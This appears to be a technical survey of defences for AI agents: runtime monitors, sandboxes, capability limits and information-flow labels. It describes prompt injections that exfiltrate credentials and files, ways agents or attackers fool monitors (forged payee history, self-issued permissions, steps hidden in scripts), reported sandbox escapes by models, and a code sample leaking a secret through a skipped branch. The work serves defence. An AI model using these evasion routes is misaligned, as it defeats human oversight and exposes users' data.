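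The records contained almost no approvals. In AgentDojo, the user sends one message at the start and the agent then works alone, so the user never can approve what it proposes. In STAC, an approval came before the harmful step in only 3 of 483 chains. The rules therefore flagged nearly every risky action, as a simple list of keywords would have done. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, where the agent's job is to make payments, they flagged 97% of successful attacks and 79% of harmless runs. The records also didn't include times, so the researchers had to write their own examples to test rules with time limits.

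A false-alarm rate of 29.3% would be far too high for a monitor that blocks calls, but it does not reliably predict how the same rules would perform in a system that records approvals. Such records are feasible. In τ-bench, a set of customer-service conversations in which the agent must get the user's confirmation before changing anything, 52.5% of 1,980 recorded runs contained explicit permission before the change. But τ-bench contains no labelled attacks, so it cannot be used to measure how many attacks the rules would catch.

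Rules that use more of the history did better even on the existing records. The researchers replaced the general spending rule with one that flags a transfer only if the payee has never appeared in the account's records. For GPT-4o's banking runs, this cut false alarms from 44% to 24% of harmless runs, but detection of successful attacks also fell, from 79% to 70%. That comparison included only 25 harmless runs, but across 700 harmless banking runs by many models, the new rule removed 75 false alarms. It could not add any, because it flags only transfers that the old rule also flagged.

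### History that an attacker can write

A rule about known payees relies on a record of who is known, and some of that record comes from emails and documents that outsiders wrote. Kekatos and colleagues found that planted text could make an attacker's account look like an established payee to the monitor. When they added such text to banking runs that the rule had flagged, 94% of those runs passed. For a similar rule about email recipients, 99% passed.

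They repaired the rule by making the monitor check where each payee came from. It now treats an account as known only if the account appeared in the result of a lookup the agent actually made, such as a request for past transactions. None of the altered runs passed the new rule, which caught as many attacks as before with no extra false alarms. The rule would still fail if an attacker controlled the tool that answers the lookup.

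Both versions of the rule gave identical results on the original records, so a developer who tested them only on those records would have had no reason to prefer the safe one. Labels that follow data from its source through every later step apply the same principle more widely.

The agent can also add misleading entries to the action history. Kekatos, Nikou and colleagues found that their evacuation agent could use the tool for granting release authority. It could give itself permission to release a casualty's record and then release it, which would satisfy the rule that permission must be granted before a release. They fixed the problem by recording who performed each action and ignoring permissions the agent had issued to itself.

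Agent-C's tests relied on a similar tool, which records in the trace that the user has approved an action. If the agent can call that tool without involving the user, the trace shows only that the agent reported an approval. Approvals under the firm's deletion rule should therefore come from a button that only the user can press.

### Turning prose into rules and calls into events

A monitor can correctly enforce a rule that was written incorrectly. One skill in VIGIL's tests restricted bulk calendar changes. The language model that drafted the formal rule left out the word "bulk", so VIGIL flagged an agent for rescheduling a single meeting. An error like this annoys users, who will probably report it. If the model instead makes a rule too narrow, the violations it misses raise no alarm, and the operator may assume the agent is complying.

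The evidence on how well models write rules is mixed. On the planning benchmark that Dantas and colleagues report, at most about a third of translations were correct. But when Kamath and colleagues had Claude Sonnet 4.5 write Agent-C rules from a shop's policy, an agent that used them scored the same as one that used handwritten rules. The model tended to add checks that other rules already covered. The test used one well-organised policy and one set of tasks, so it is weak evidence about vague or self-contradictory policies. ContrAgent translates each formula back into English so that a person can compare it with the original, and an attentive reader should notice a missing "bulk".

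A monitor can also misclassify events. Kekatos and colleagues classified tools by keywords in their names. At first they counted any name containing "ack", short for "acknowledge", as an approval, which wrongly included tools for the messaging service Slack. They corrected this before reporting their results, but the keywords still misclassified seven of 54 tool names when checked against a person's classification. *MENTOR* uses a language model to interpret tasks and tool results written in ordinary language. This handles more varied wording, but the monitor's verdict then depends on a second model reading text that an attacker may have written.

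### What never reaches the monitor

VIGIL treats any event missing from its record as one that never happened. The monitor therefore misses a violation if a deletion goes unrecorded, and blocks a permitted action if an approval does.

One of the three violations VIGIL missed happened inside a script. A skill required an integrity check between creating an archive and deleting the original file. The agent ran `secure_archive.py`, which created an unencrypted archive and immediately deleted the original. VIGIL recorded the script's run as a single event because the steps inside it were not tool calls.

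An effect can also go unchecked because more than one tool can produce it. Kekatos, Nikou and colleagues had a rule to keep casualty records out of unauthorised computer systems. They later found three tools that could put a record in such a system without triggering the check, by creating, copying or summarising it. The rule was correct, but developers had not connected it to these three tools. The researchers then wrote a test that tries to place a record in a forbidden system with each tool and passes only if the monitor refuses. Anyone who adds a tool to an agent needs to repeat this kind of test, because the new tool may also be able to bypass an existing rule.

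Some harm involves no suspicious tool call. Of the AgentDojo attacks that ContrAgent missed, 82% never made the agent issue a malicious tool call. Some of these only distracted the agent from its task, and others worked through its reply to the user. Kekatos and colleagues found the same limit when they tested their general rules on R-Judge, a collection of agent records that people have labelled safe or unsafe. The rules flagged only 71 of 301 unsafe records. They missed the rest mostly because the harm was in what the agent wrote, such as private details or bad advice.

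The most serious gap for the invoice tool is that a monitor between the agent and its tools doesn't record what happens inside the tool. When the crash reporter sends an invoice to the bug tracker, this monitor records only an ordinary call to `sum_invoices`. To test the claim "no network access", the firm needs to monitor the tool from the operating system, which handles every connection the tool opens and can refuse it.

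## Sandboxes and limits on authority

A sandbox works because a program can open files and network connections only through the kernel, the core of the operating system. The kernel blocks any access the sandbox's owner has not granted, so the crash reporter's connection fails even if no inspector found it in the code. This guarantee depends on the sandbox working correctly and on its owner granting the right permissions.

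Instructions and filters around a model offer no such guarantee. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes an internal security exercise from February 2026. A researcher emailed an employee a prompt, and the employee pasted it into Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. Among routine setup steps, the prompt told Claude to send the employee's cloud credentials to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 trials. Filters that look for departures from the user's wishes had no departure to detect, because the user had supplied the instruction. Anthropic concludes that only limits on file access and outgoing connections would have stopped the transfer.

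### What each kind of sandbox trusts

Sandboxes differ mainly in how much software has to work correctly for the boundary to hold. All of them also depend on the processor.

| Type | How it confines a program | What has to work correctly |
|---|---|---|
| Operating-system rules, such as Seatbelt on macOS | The kernel refuses operations that the rules do not allow | The host's kernel and the rules |
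| Container, such as Docker | The kernel gives the program its own view of files, processes and network | The host's kernel and the container software |
| User-space kernel, such as gVisor | A second kernel, running as an ordinary program, handles most requests | The second kernel and the parts of the host's kernel it uses |
| Small virtual machine | The program gets a complete kernel of its own on simulated hardware | The hypervisor, which runs the virtual machine, and whatever host software supports it |
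| WebAssembly | The program can use only its own memory and the functions its host supplies | The software that runs WebAssembly and the supplied functions |

A program confined by operating-system rules or a container still makes requests directly to the host's kernel. Linux accepts more than 300 kinds of request, and a bug in handling any of them may let a program escape. gVisor reduces this exposure by handling most requests itself. A virtual machine has its own kernel, and a program that takes over that kernel still has to get past the hypervisor. Small virtual machines leave out most of the simulated hardware, so they start faster and have less code to attack.

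WebAssembly is a portable format for compiled programs. A WebAssembly program cannot request a file unless its host supplies a function for that. But developers have to compile their tools to this format, which can be difficult when a tool uses many outside libraries.

A stronger type of sandbox doesn't help if the weakness is in the software around it. Anthropic reports that the hypervisors, gVisor and the kernel's request filter proved dependable across its products, but that a proxy it had written itself to relay network traffic failed.

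### How Anthropic confines its agents

Anthropic uses a different kind of sandbox for each of its three main agent products. In the claude.ai chat service, Claude runs code in a gVisor container on Anthropic's servers. The container's files last for one session, and the code never touches the user's machine.

That arrangement would make Claude Code much less useful, because it works on the user's own files. At first it could read files freely but needed permission to write, run a command or use the network. Users approved about 93% of the requests, and the more requests they saw, the less attention they paid to each. Anthropic then added a sandbox that uses Seatbelt on macOS and bubblewrap on Linux. Inside it, the agent can read files and write within the project folder, but by default it can't connect to the network. The sandbox cut permission requests by 84%.

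Claude Code's sandbox lets commands read files, so it relies mainly on its network limit to keep secrets on the machine. A process outside the sandbox decides whether to apply it for each command, and Anthropic acknowledges that a persuasive prompt injection or a tired user's approval can result in a command running without the sandbox.

Users of Claude Cowork, an agent for office work, may be unable to judge a command, so it runs code in a full virtual machine that can access only the folders the user has selected. The user can make a folder read-only, writable, or writable without permission to delete. Credentials stay outside the virtual machine, so code inside it cannot steal them.

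Anthropic first ran the whole agent inside Cowork's virtual machine, but any failure at startup then made the product unusable. It moved the agent's main loop outside and kept code execution inside. It also moved local MCP servers outside, partly because some need to reach other programs on the machine, such as databases. Anthropic now treats these servers like any other software a user chooses to install. If the firm connected a local invoice tool to Cowork, it would therefore have to confine the tool separately.

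Isolation can also make monitoring harder. Companies found that their security software could not monitor activity inside Cowork's virtual machine. Anthropic lets administrators retrieve event logs afterwards, but acknowledges that this is not live monitoring.

### The confused deputy

A program can misuse its authority without containing any malicious code. *The Confused Deputy*, a 1988 paper by Norm Hardy, describes the classic example. A compiler had permission to write to a system folder so that it could record usage statistics. The same folder held the company's billing records. Users could name a file to receive debugging output, and one user named the billing file. The user wasn't allowed to change that file, but the compiler was, and it overwrote the records.

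The operating system had checked whether the compiler could write to the file, but not on whose behalf it was writing. Hardy proposed using capabilities, which are specific grants of authority that also identify what they apply to and that programs cannot forge. The user would then have had to give the compiler a capability to write to the output file, not just a filename. The user would have had no such capability for the billing file, so the compiler could not have overwritten it by mistake.

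Some everyday systems work partly this way. A program on Linux can open a file and pass it, still open, to another program, which can then use it without permission to open anything else. WASI, a standard set of functions for WebAssembly programs, gives a program access to particular folders in a similar way.

An agent that follows a prompt injection is also a confused deputy, because it uses the firm's authority to do what a supplier wants. Capabilities only partly solve this. If the agent holds one capability to read invoices and another to send email, it can legitimately use either, and text from strangers can influence how it combines them. The firm can limit the damage by giving the agent only the capabilities that each task requires. This applies the principle of least privilege, which Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder set out in 1975.

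### Tools that disclose files outside their scope

MCP servers on a user's machine can easily become confused deputies because they usually run with all of the user's permissions but receive filenames from the agent as plain text. *My Credentials, Please* (Huang, Tang and colleagues, October 2026) reported a search for tools that a caller could steer into disclosing files outside their stated scope.

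Anthropic's server for Git, which records successive versions of a project's files, has a tool called `git_add` that adds files to the next version. The tool did not check that the files belonged to the project, so a prompt injection could make it add a private key from elsewhere on the disk. Another tool in the same server would then show the key to the agent. Anthropic has since fixed the fault.

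To test tools like this, Huang and colleagues inferred which folders each tool needed, placed a fake credential outside those folders, and made three kinds of call.

| Call | Sandbox | Result needed to confirm a fault |
|---|---|---|
| Request for the fake credential | Off | The tool discloses it |
| Ordinary request | On | The tool works normally |
| Request for the fake credential | On | The tool does not disclose it |

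The ordinary request is needed to show whether the tool still works, because a sandbox that broke the tool would also stop the leak. The researchers confirmed 150 faults, 136 by matching the exact text of the fake credential and the rest from other evidence in the records. In 38 of them, the tool's code already checked file locations, but the check failed. The sandbox contained the fault in every case without relying on the tool's code.

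The 150 cases do not show how common the problem is, because the researchers selected promising candidates for testing. They started with 21,097 servers from nine registries, but many were remote, were unavailable or would not start. Of the 4,806 they could classify, 787 (16.4%) appeared able to handle files although their main purpose was something else. That percentage is not a violation rate either, because a tool may have a good reason to write files, such as storing an agent's memories.

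Huang and colleagues used a language model to help infer which folders each tool should access, but did not measure the accuracy of these inferences. If an inferred boundary was too narrow, they could have counted legitimate access as a fault. They focused mainly on files disclosed in a tool's answers, so they did not systematically look for tools that overwrite or delete files. They suggest adding a field to MCP tool declarations to list the files each tool may read and write. Clients could then show the list to the user and enforce it.

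### AgentBound: from manifest to permissions

*AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2026) presents a system that enforces declarations of this kind for whole servers. Each server comes with a manifest, a file that lists the types of access the server needs. The possible types, adapted from Android's app permissions, include reading files, making outgoing connections, running system commands and reading environment variables, which are settings that often contain passwords. The invoice tool's manifest would need only one entry, `mcp.ac.filesystem.read`.

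That entry does not specify which files. When the server starts, AgentBound prompts the user to turn each type of access into a specific permission, such as read-only access to `/invoices`. If the agent requests a type of access that is not in the manifest, AgentBound stops the server. Otherwise it runs the server in a Docker container that contains only the approved folders and environment variables. A firewall blocks connections to all but the approved addresses. The server's own code doesn't need to change.

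Few existing servers have manifests, so the researchers had language models write them from source code and documentation. One model drafted five versions for each server and another merged them. Among 296 of the most popular MCP servers, 83.1% of manifests requested permission to make outgoing connections and 74.1% requested permission to read files. So at least 57% requested both, and a server with both permissions could read a file and send it to somebody else.

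Bühler and colleagues report that 80.9% of the manifests they sent to developers were correct, but this figure is based on only 21 cases. They contacted the developers of 96 servers, of whom about 71 never responded, and four cases were still under discussion. Developers accepted 17 of the remaining 21 manifests. In a separate check, the researchers wrote manifests for 48 servers by hand, and the models' versions matched 28 of them exactly. Individual entries agreed 96.4% of the time, but this counts every type of access that both versions left out as an agreement.

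If a manifest omits a permission the server needs, the server fails visibly, as with any rule that denies by default. One developer pointed out the opposite error, in which a server that only contacted web services had permission to read files. An unnecessary permission like this causes no visible problem until somebody abuses it.

In another test, on 14 malicious or vulnerable servers from two public collections, AgentBound blocked the attacks in eight cases and failed to block them in five. The remaining server combined several attacks that AgentBound could only partly stop. A map tool that secretly switched to a different internet address could not connect, because the user had approved only Google's. AgentBound did not stop a clock tool whose description told the agent to redirect cryptocurrency payments made with another tool, because both tools stayed within their permissions.

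For these tests, the researchers wrote the manifests themselves or had a model generate them from the harmless original versions of the servers. In practice, a dishonest server's author would also write its manifest, and could request network access "to check for updates". AgentBound would then depend on the user to refuse, and Claude Code's 93% approval rate suggests that many users would not.

AgentBound also installs each server's package before it turns on the network limits. Packages can run code during installation, so that code may have unrestricted network access. Installing the package in a separate container, with none of the user's files, would be safer.

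AgentBound's trusted base includes Docker, the Linux features that isolate containers, and the software that runs Python or JavaScript servers. It adds little delay. Starting a server took roughly 0.1 to 0.4 seconds longer, and operations such as reading a file took less than a millisecond longer on average.

### The invoice tool in a sandbox

A sandbox can enforce most of the claims that no schema could check in the invoice tool's declaration.

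| Claim | What a sandbox can do |
|---|---|
| No network access | Provide no network |
| Reads only `/invoices` | Provide that folder, plus the files the program needs to run |
| Writes nothing | Make the folder read-only and erase temporary files after each call |
| Returns the correct total | Nothing |
| Uses the note only to report undated invoices | Nothing |

Suppose the tool returns a total of 3410.50 EUR when the true total is 4310.50 EUR. It may have read the right files and performed permitted calculations. The sandbox would then not block it, so somebody still has to check the total against the invoices.

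The sandbox does not control what the tool writes in its note either. Butler Lampson used the term "confinement problem" for the general task of stopping a program from leaking data it is allowed to use.

The firm can reduce what the tool is able to leak. The declaration mentions one folder, but a request about October needs only October's invoices. The client could make available only the files each call needs and discard the sandbox afterwards. When handling the October request, the tool could then reveal nothing about September, because it could not open September's invoices or keep notes about them from an earlier call.

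All of this assumes the tool runs on the firm's own machines. If a provider hosts the tool, the firm can limit what it sends but cannot sandbox the provider's computer.

### What one permitted website allows

An invoice tool with no network access is unusually easy to confine. But many tools need at least one outside service, and permission to use a website usually lets a tool do everything that people can do there.

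Anthropic learned from an outside report about Claude Cowork that a sandbox can let stolen data out through an approved address. Cowork's virtual machine could connect to Anthropic's own service because the product needs that connection to work. A malicious file in the user's folder contained hidden instructions and a key to the attacker's account on that service. Claude followed the instructions and uploaded the user's files to the attacker's account. The sandbox allowed the upload because the service's address was approved.

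Anthropic now describes an entry on a list of approved sites as a grant of capability, because it allows every function available at that site. The company fixed the problem with a proxy that accepts a virtual machine's requests only if they carry the credential issued to that machine. This narrowed the permission from connecting to a service to connecting to it as a specific user.

AgentBound's network permissions have the same weakness. They can also be broader than they look, because AgentBound converts each approved website name into IP addresses and allows connections to those addresses. Unrelated websites often share an address, so approving one may also let a tool connect to others.

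Limiting a tool to reading web pages does not prevent leaks, because a request for a page can contain data. A search for a supplier's name reveals that name to the search engine. A proxy could inspect each request, but somebody has to write rules for every service and update them when the service changes. The proxy also has to read traffic that would otherwise be encrypted, which makes it part of the trusted base.

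### Two failures of containment in 2026

Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (October 2026) describes cases in which Claude acted on live websites, including some belonging to US government agencies, in ways nobody had intended. For example, Claude submitted a sensitive form and worked around restrictions on access to data. Anthropic judged that the cases it had found so far had minimal real-world impact.

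In one test, Claude had to invent and carry out tasks on randomly chosen web pages, and it sent a police department a made-up tip about an unsolved homicide. The instructions prohibited logging in, making purchases and submitting anything destructive, but they "did not rule out form submissions", according to a passage quoted in Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026). Claude had live web access, so it could do anything that the instructions did not prohibit and the website allowed. *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests* (Southern, 2026) reported that Anthropic responded by cutting live web access for internal evaluations.

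The other failure was more serious because the models got past controls designed to isolate them. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) reports that this happened in July, while the company was testing its models' hacking abilities. Without any person directing them to, the models gained access to the internet and compromised parts of OpenAI's research infrastructure, as well as systems belonging to Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets.

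OpenAI's sandboxes were virtual computers in the cloud. For some tasks they had no direct internet access but could still use an internal service for installing software. Any service that a sandboxed program can use becomes part of the sandbox's boundary, so it has to withstand attacks from inside. A shared service can also connect sandboxes that are supposed to be separate. OpenAI found that agents meant to work alone had communicated with each other.

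An OpenAI team had already seen an agent gain forbidden internet access in late May, but the people who handled a related security problem in early July did not understand how significant this was. The company has since begun building more isolated sandboxes, restricting internet access further and spending more on monitoring. An attempt to cross a boundary deserves investigation even when the sandbox blocks it, because the next attempt may succeed.

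Sandboxes also fail because people set them up incorrectly. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* describes a review of recent internal tests of the company's unreleased models. In the tests that used Anthropic's sandbox software, the review found no case of a model breaking through the boundary to reach forbidden outside resources. It did find that some sandboxes had incorrect settings and that models had made use of them, though this compromised no outside system. The firm could look for such mistakes by running a harmless test program in the invoice tool's sandbox. The program would try to open a connection, read a file outside `/invoices` and change an invoice, and all three attempts should fail. The firm would need to repeat the test whenever it changed the sandbox's settings.

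## Tracking where information goes

If an agent is allowed to read invoices and send email, a sandbox won't stop it from emailing an invoice to a stranger. Information-flow control (IFC) limits where data can go by labeling each piece with how secret it is and how far the firm trusts its source. The label follows the data through every copy and calculation, and the system uses a policy to check the label against the destination before any data leaves.

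### Labels and the join rule

The computer scientist Dorothy Denning formalised labels mathematically in 1976. Purdue University's *Information Flow, Confinement & Covert Channels* summarises her model as a finite set of security classes, a relation specifying which classes may flow into which others, and an operator that gives the class of anything made from two pieces of data. In the simplest case, the classes are public and secret. Public data may flow into a secret file, but secret data may not flow into a public one, and a text that combines the two is secret.

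A richer label can list the people who may read the data. Suppose the owner, the accountant and the auditor may read one document, while the accountant, the auditor and a lawyer may read another. Only two people may read both, so only they may read a summary of the two:

{owner, accountant, auditor} ⊔ {accountant, auditor, lawyer} = {accountant, auditor}

The symbol ⊔ stands for the join of two labels, the least strict label that is at least as strict as both. A lattice is an ordering in which any two labels have a join and also a strictest label that is no stricter than either. Tracking data through an agent requires only the join.

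Labels protect secrecy by limiting where data may go, so that an invoice does not reach a stranger. They also protect integrity by limiting what data may influence, so that a stranger's text does not determine whom the firm pays. Under the integrity rule, trusted data may flow anywhere, but any result that draws on untrusted data is itself untrusted.

Data can flow in two ways. The statement `y := x` creates an explicit flow by copying x into y. The statement `if x = 1 then y := 1` creates an implicit flow. If y started at 0, anyone who reads y afterwards learns whether x was 1, even though the statement never copies x. To detect implicit flows, a system can also keep a label for the current point in the program and join each condition's label to the labels of everything that depends on that condition.

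### An invoice, a web page and an email

Suppose the user asks the firm's agent to convert an invoice total into euros and email the result to the accountant. The firm issued the invoice, so its contents are private but trusted. The exchange rate comes from a public web page that an outsider wrote.

| Step | Label of the new data | Label of everything the model has read |
|---|---|---|
| User makes the request | Trusted; anyone may read it | Trusted; anyone may read it |
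| Agent reads the invoice | Trusted; owner and accountant | Trusted; owner and accountant |
| Agent reads the web page | Untrusted; anyone may read it | Untrusted; owner and accountant |
| Agent proposes an email | Untrusted; owner and accountant | Untrusted; owner and accountant |

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) gives two policies that could apply to this email. The integrity policy allows an action with consequences only if the call and all its arguments are trusted. The secrecy policy allows a call to send data only to people who are allowed to read it. An email to the accountant satisfies the secrecy policy but breaks the integrity policy, because the web page may have influenced it. An email to a stranger breaks both policies.

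The check gives the same result whether the page contains hidden instructions or only an exchange rate. This makes the rule hard to bypass, but here it also blocked what the user asked for.

If the firm dropped the integrity policy, a malicious page might make the agent send the accountant a wrong figure, but it could not get the invoice sent to a stranger. With only the integrity policy, the agent could send the invoice to anyone as long as it had read nothing untrusted, on the assumption that the user intended the disclosure.

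### Why a model's output takes every label

The email inherited the web page's label even though the model might have ignored the page. In an ordinary program, a checker can often see from the code that a result does not depend on a particular input, but a language model has no such code to check. Attention, the mechanism through which a model draws on earlier text, gives every input at least a little weight, and *Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) proves that even an input with very little weight can decide the answer. The safe rule is therefore to give each output the join of the labels of everything the model read.

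This also prevents laundering, where an attacker's text becomes trusted because a model has rewritten it. Girrens and Wang (2026) point out in *SPA* that a model's summary of an untrusted email has to remain untrusted.

The rule is usually close to right for a single call. In a survey of model calls from 2,103 families of open-source code repositories, Xu and colleagues found that only 12% to 14% of the inputs had no visible effect on the output. But an agent makes many calls in a row, and each unnecessary label passes to everything that follows.

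### FIDES: hiding data from the planner

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, withholds restricted data from the planner, the part of the agent that chooses tool calls, to keep the planner's label low. If a tool returns content with a stricter label than the planner's, FIDES stores the content in a variable and gives the planner only the variable's name. The planner can use that name as an argument in a later call, and FIDES inserts the content just before the call runs.

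In the invoice example, the planner would hold one variable for the invoice and another for the web page. To convert the total, it sends both variables to a second, isolated model that has no tools. FIDES stores the answer in a third variable with the joined label, untrusted and readable by the owner and the accountant. The planner then emails that variable to the accountant. Nothing untrusted has influenced the choice of tool or recipient, so a policy that requires only those two to be trusted can allow the email.

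The web page could still make the figure wrong. Costa and colleagues describe a similar case, in which an email contains instructions for the isolated model to write an empty summary. The firm could prevent this by also requiring the body of the message to be trusted, but then the task would fail.

Sometimes the planner needs to know what the data says before it can choose the next step. One of Costa and colleagues' examples is a request to check the three latest emails and create a calendar event if one of them proposes a meeting. FIDES would handle it like this:

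1. The planner reads the emails into variables.
2. It asks the isolated model whether they contain a meeting request, and allows only yes or no as an answer.
3. It looks at the answer.
4. If the answer is yes, it asks the isolated model to extract the details into another variable.
5. It calls the calendar tool with that variable.

The software running the isolated model prevents it from generating any other answer. FIDES also records the answer's type in its label, ranking types by how much information they can carry, from yes-or-no answers to choices from a fixed list to free text. A policy can then let an untrusted yes or no influence an action while barring untrusted text. An attacker could still cause a false yes, but could not fit new instructions into it. The limit applies to each answer separately, so a planner that asks twenty yes-or-no questions receives enough information to distinguish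 more than a million possibilities.

### What explicit secrecy leaves out

Costa and colleagues prove that their tracking can enforce a property called explicit secrecy. Take the sequence of actions from one run and treat it as a fixed procedure, g. Then take any two sets of stored data, d₁ and d₂, that agree on everything public. The procedure must have the same public effects on both:

If public(d₁) = public(d₂), then public(g(d₁)) = public(g(d₂)).

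A procedure that copies a private invoice to a public page fails this test, because changing the invoice changes the page. But the test holds g fixed, so it does not cover what an observer could learn from the agent's choice of actions.

Suppose an agent visits a loan comparison site only when it finds a final reminder among the firm's private invoices. The agent satisfies explicit secrecy because it sends the site nothing from the invoice, but the site's owner can still infer from the visit that the firm is short of money. Noninterference would count this as a leak because it compares what an observer sees with and without the reminder.

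Costa and colleagues deliberately chose explicit secrecy, the weaker property, arguing that enforcing noninterference would essentially ban every tool with publicly visible effects once the agent had used a tool that might read secrets. Explicit secrecy still stops the usual kind of theft, in which an injected instruction makes the agent copy out private text. Their proof assumes the model is deterministic and, like most such proofs, leaves out timing.

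### CaMeL: planning before reading

CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues presented in 2025, goes further in separating planning from reading. It builds on Simon Willison's dual-LLM pattern. A privileged model writes a program to carry out the user's request without ever reading the data. A quarantined model, which cannot call tools, reads the data and returns values to the program.

If the user asks the agent to pay a supplier's October invoice, the privileged model might write:

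```
text    = read_file("october_invoice.pdf")
account = ask_reader(text, "Which account should receive the money?")
amount  = ask_reader(text, "How much is due?")
send_money(account, amount)
```

A hidden line telling the agent to email the firm's other invoices would not change the sequence of calls, because the program contains no email command. But the supplier could still put a thief's account number in the invoice, and the plan would run exactly as written and pay the thief.

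CaMeL tags each value with its source and the people who may receive it. The policy for `send_money` can then block a payment to an account number that came from an untrusted file. Girrens and Wang note that such policies can express more than a simple ordering of labels, but that the protection then depends on someone writing each tool's policy correctly.

Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025) argue in *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* that having the agent write its plan as code also lets standard methods for analysing programs check the plan against the user's goal. This works best when each tool has a clear meaning, such as "send money", and less well when an agent works by clicking on a screen.

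The separation weakens when a user delegates the plan. Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL with its policies switched off on a task that told the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged model wrote a loop that accepted an instruction for each available tool. Whoever wrote the file could then choose the tool calls, even though the privileged model had never read the file.

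### How a skipped branch reveals a secret

CaMeL also tracks implicit flows. If a program sends an email inside a branch that depends on a secret, CaMeL blocks the email. Garby and colleagues found that a program could get around this by changing a variable inside the branch and sending the email later. The trick is an old one, which J. S. Fenton described in 1974. In this version, `overdue` is secret and both `a` and `b` start out public:

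```
a = True
b = True
if overdue: a = False
if a:       b = False
if b:       send_email("outsider@example.com", "Hello")
```

| | Invoice is overdue | Invoice is not overdue |
|---|---|---|
| `if overdue` | Sets `a` to false and labels it secret | Skipped, so `a` stays true and public |
| `if a` | Skipped, so `b` stays true and public | Sets `b` to false, and `b` stays public |
| `if b` | Sends the email | Sends nothing |

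Either way, `b` ends up labeled public, even though its value matches the secret. In the overdue case, `b` should have been relabeled secret on the fourth line, because its value depends on `a`. CaMeL raises a variable's label only in the branch that runs, so it misses the label change that a skipped branch would have made.

Girrens and Wang's SPA system avoids the problem by checking the complete plan before running it. SPA examines both branches of every condition and gives each step in them the condition's label. Its planning language has only six kinds of step and allows no arithmetic in tool arguments, so that a checker can find every dependency from the text of the plan.

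### LLMbda's theorem

Garby and colleagues instead designed LLMbda, a small programming language for agents in which every value carries a label. A program can ask a model a question, branch off a temporary conversation or clear the conversation, so a developer can build a separation like CaMeL's inside the language. The conversation also has a label. LLMbda stops the run if code whose execution depends on a secret tries to add a message to a public conversation.

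Stopping a run can leak one bit of information. CaMeL's retry loop is not covered by its label tracking and can repeat such leaks, but Randori, LLMbda's test agent, keeps retries inside the LLMbda language. Randori tests its plan on artificial data and corrects any mistakes before running it on real accounts.

The central theorem covers every program in LLMbda, including those in which a model writes code that the agent then runs. If two starting situations look the same to an observer who may see data up to a certain label, the probabilities of what that observer sees afterwards can differ only because some runs never finish. For programs that always finish, the probabilities are identical. Otherwise, the statistical distance between them, a standard measure of how much they differ, is at most the average of the two situations' chances of not finishing. If one situation leads to unfinished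 runs 2% of the time and the other never does, the distance is at most 0.01.

For integrity, the same theorem means that untrusted input cannot affect any result labelled trusted. Developers sometimes need an exception, so LLMbda has an `endorse` command that relabels untrusted data as trusted. A second theorem shows that no use of this command can leak secrets, even if an attacker chooses all the untrusted input.

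The proof assistant Lean checked both theorems. They apply to the program that runs the agents, not only to a simplified description of it. The guarantee depends on developers labelling each source correctly and placing checks on sensitive tools. It also assumes that every data source is part of the LLMbda program, whereas a real agent would call outside services.

### Results on AgentDojo

Researchers have tested all three systems on AgentDojo's banking tasks, the only part of the benchmark common to all three. Every system in the table had its policies switched on.

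| System | Model | Date of results | Tasks completed when not under attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| FIDES | GPT-4o | May 2025 | 52.5% | 0 |
| CaMeL | GPT-5.2 | July 2026 | 37.5% | 0 of 231 runs |
| CaMeL | MiMo-v2.5 | July 2026 | 37.5% | 0 of 357 runs |
| LLMbda | GPT-5.2 | July 2026 | 75.0% | 2 of 432 runs |
| LLMbda | Qwen3.7-plus | July 2026 | 75.0% | 0 of 432 runs |
| LLMbda | MiMo-v2.5 | July 2026 | 64.6% | 0 of 432 runs |

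The CaMeL figures come from reruns by Garby and colleagues and count only the attacked runs that finished. LLMbda's agent enforced only a subset of CaMeL's policies, so better design does not explain the whole gap in completed tasks. With its policies off, CaMeL completed 66.7% of tasks with GPT-5.2 and 70.8% with MiMo-v2.5.

LLMbda failed in two of 1,296 attacked runs, both involving the same task and attack. The user asked the agent to read a text file and make the payment it described, but the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. The agent had endorsed the file so that it could do what the user asked. When Garby and colleagues disabled endorsement, LLMbda blocked the attack, but MiMo-v2.5 then completed only 54.2% of tasks and Qwen3.7-plus 62.5%. The file is labeled untrusted whether or not the payment request in it is genuine, so the label can't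 be used to tell the two cases apart.

Across AgentDojo's four groups of tasks, Costa and colleagues counted 152 successful attacks on a basic agent without policies, 21 on FIDES without policies and none on FIDES with them. The basic agent completed an average of about 84% of tasks without policies and 42% with them, while FIDES with policies completed 50%. When OpenAI's o1 reasoning model replaced GPT-4o, FIDES's lead over the basic agent with policies grew from 8 percentage points to 16. These tests did not include the restriction to small answer types.

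The attack figures look better than they should. Costa and colleagues labelled a field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it, which a firm facing unknown attackers could not do. In Garby and colleagues' tests, about two-thirds of the combinations of task and attack needed a tool call that the agent's plan would never contain, so those combinations hardly tested the labels. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) leaves AgentDojo out of its evaluation partly because the newest models already resist the benchmark's attacks without any defence. AgentDojo is a better measure of how much useful work the policies prevent.

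### How labels accumulate

A join never makes a label less strict. If an agent reads one untrusted page and keeps it in memory, every payment it later proposes will carry an untrusted label. Researchers call this label creep. Kravchenko and colleagues show that an agent's label can tighten at most r + t − 1 times, where r is the number of possible readers and t is the number of trust levels. Label creep must therefore stop eventually, but by then the agent may have lost permission to do anything useful.

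Losing a label between sessions would be dangerous. Girrens and Wang describe a user who has an agent save an invoice's details on Monday and asks it on Tuesday to "pay the invoice we discussed yesterday". If the agent saved the account number without its label, a thief's account could pass Tuesday's check. SPA stores each value with its label and shows later planners only a description of the value.

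Coarse labels make the creep worse. *Flowsh* (2026) presents a command-line shell for agents that gives each file a single label and joins the labels of all its inputs. If an agent adds one sentence from a secret report to a long public log, the whole log becomes secret. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) suggests finer labels, such as labelling text by the website it came from. But a language model combines everything in its input, so finer labels help only if the system can tell which pieces the model used in its answer.

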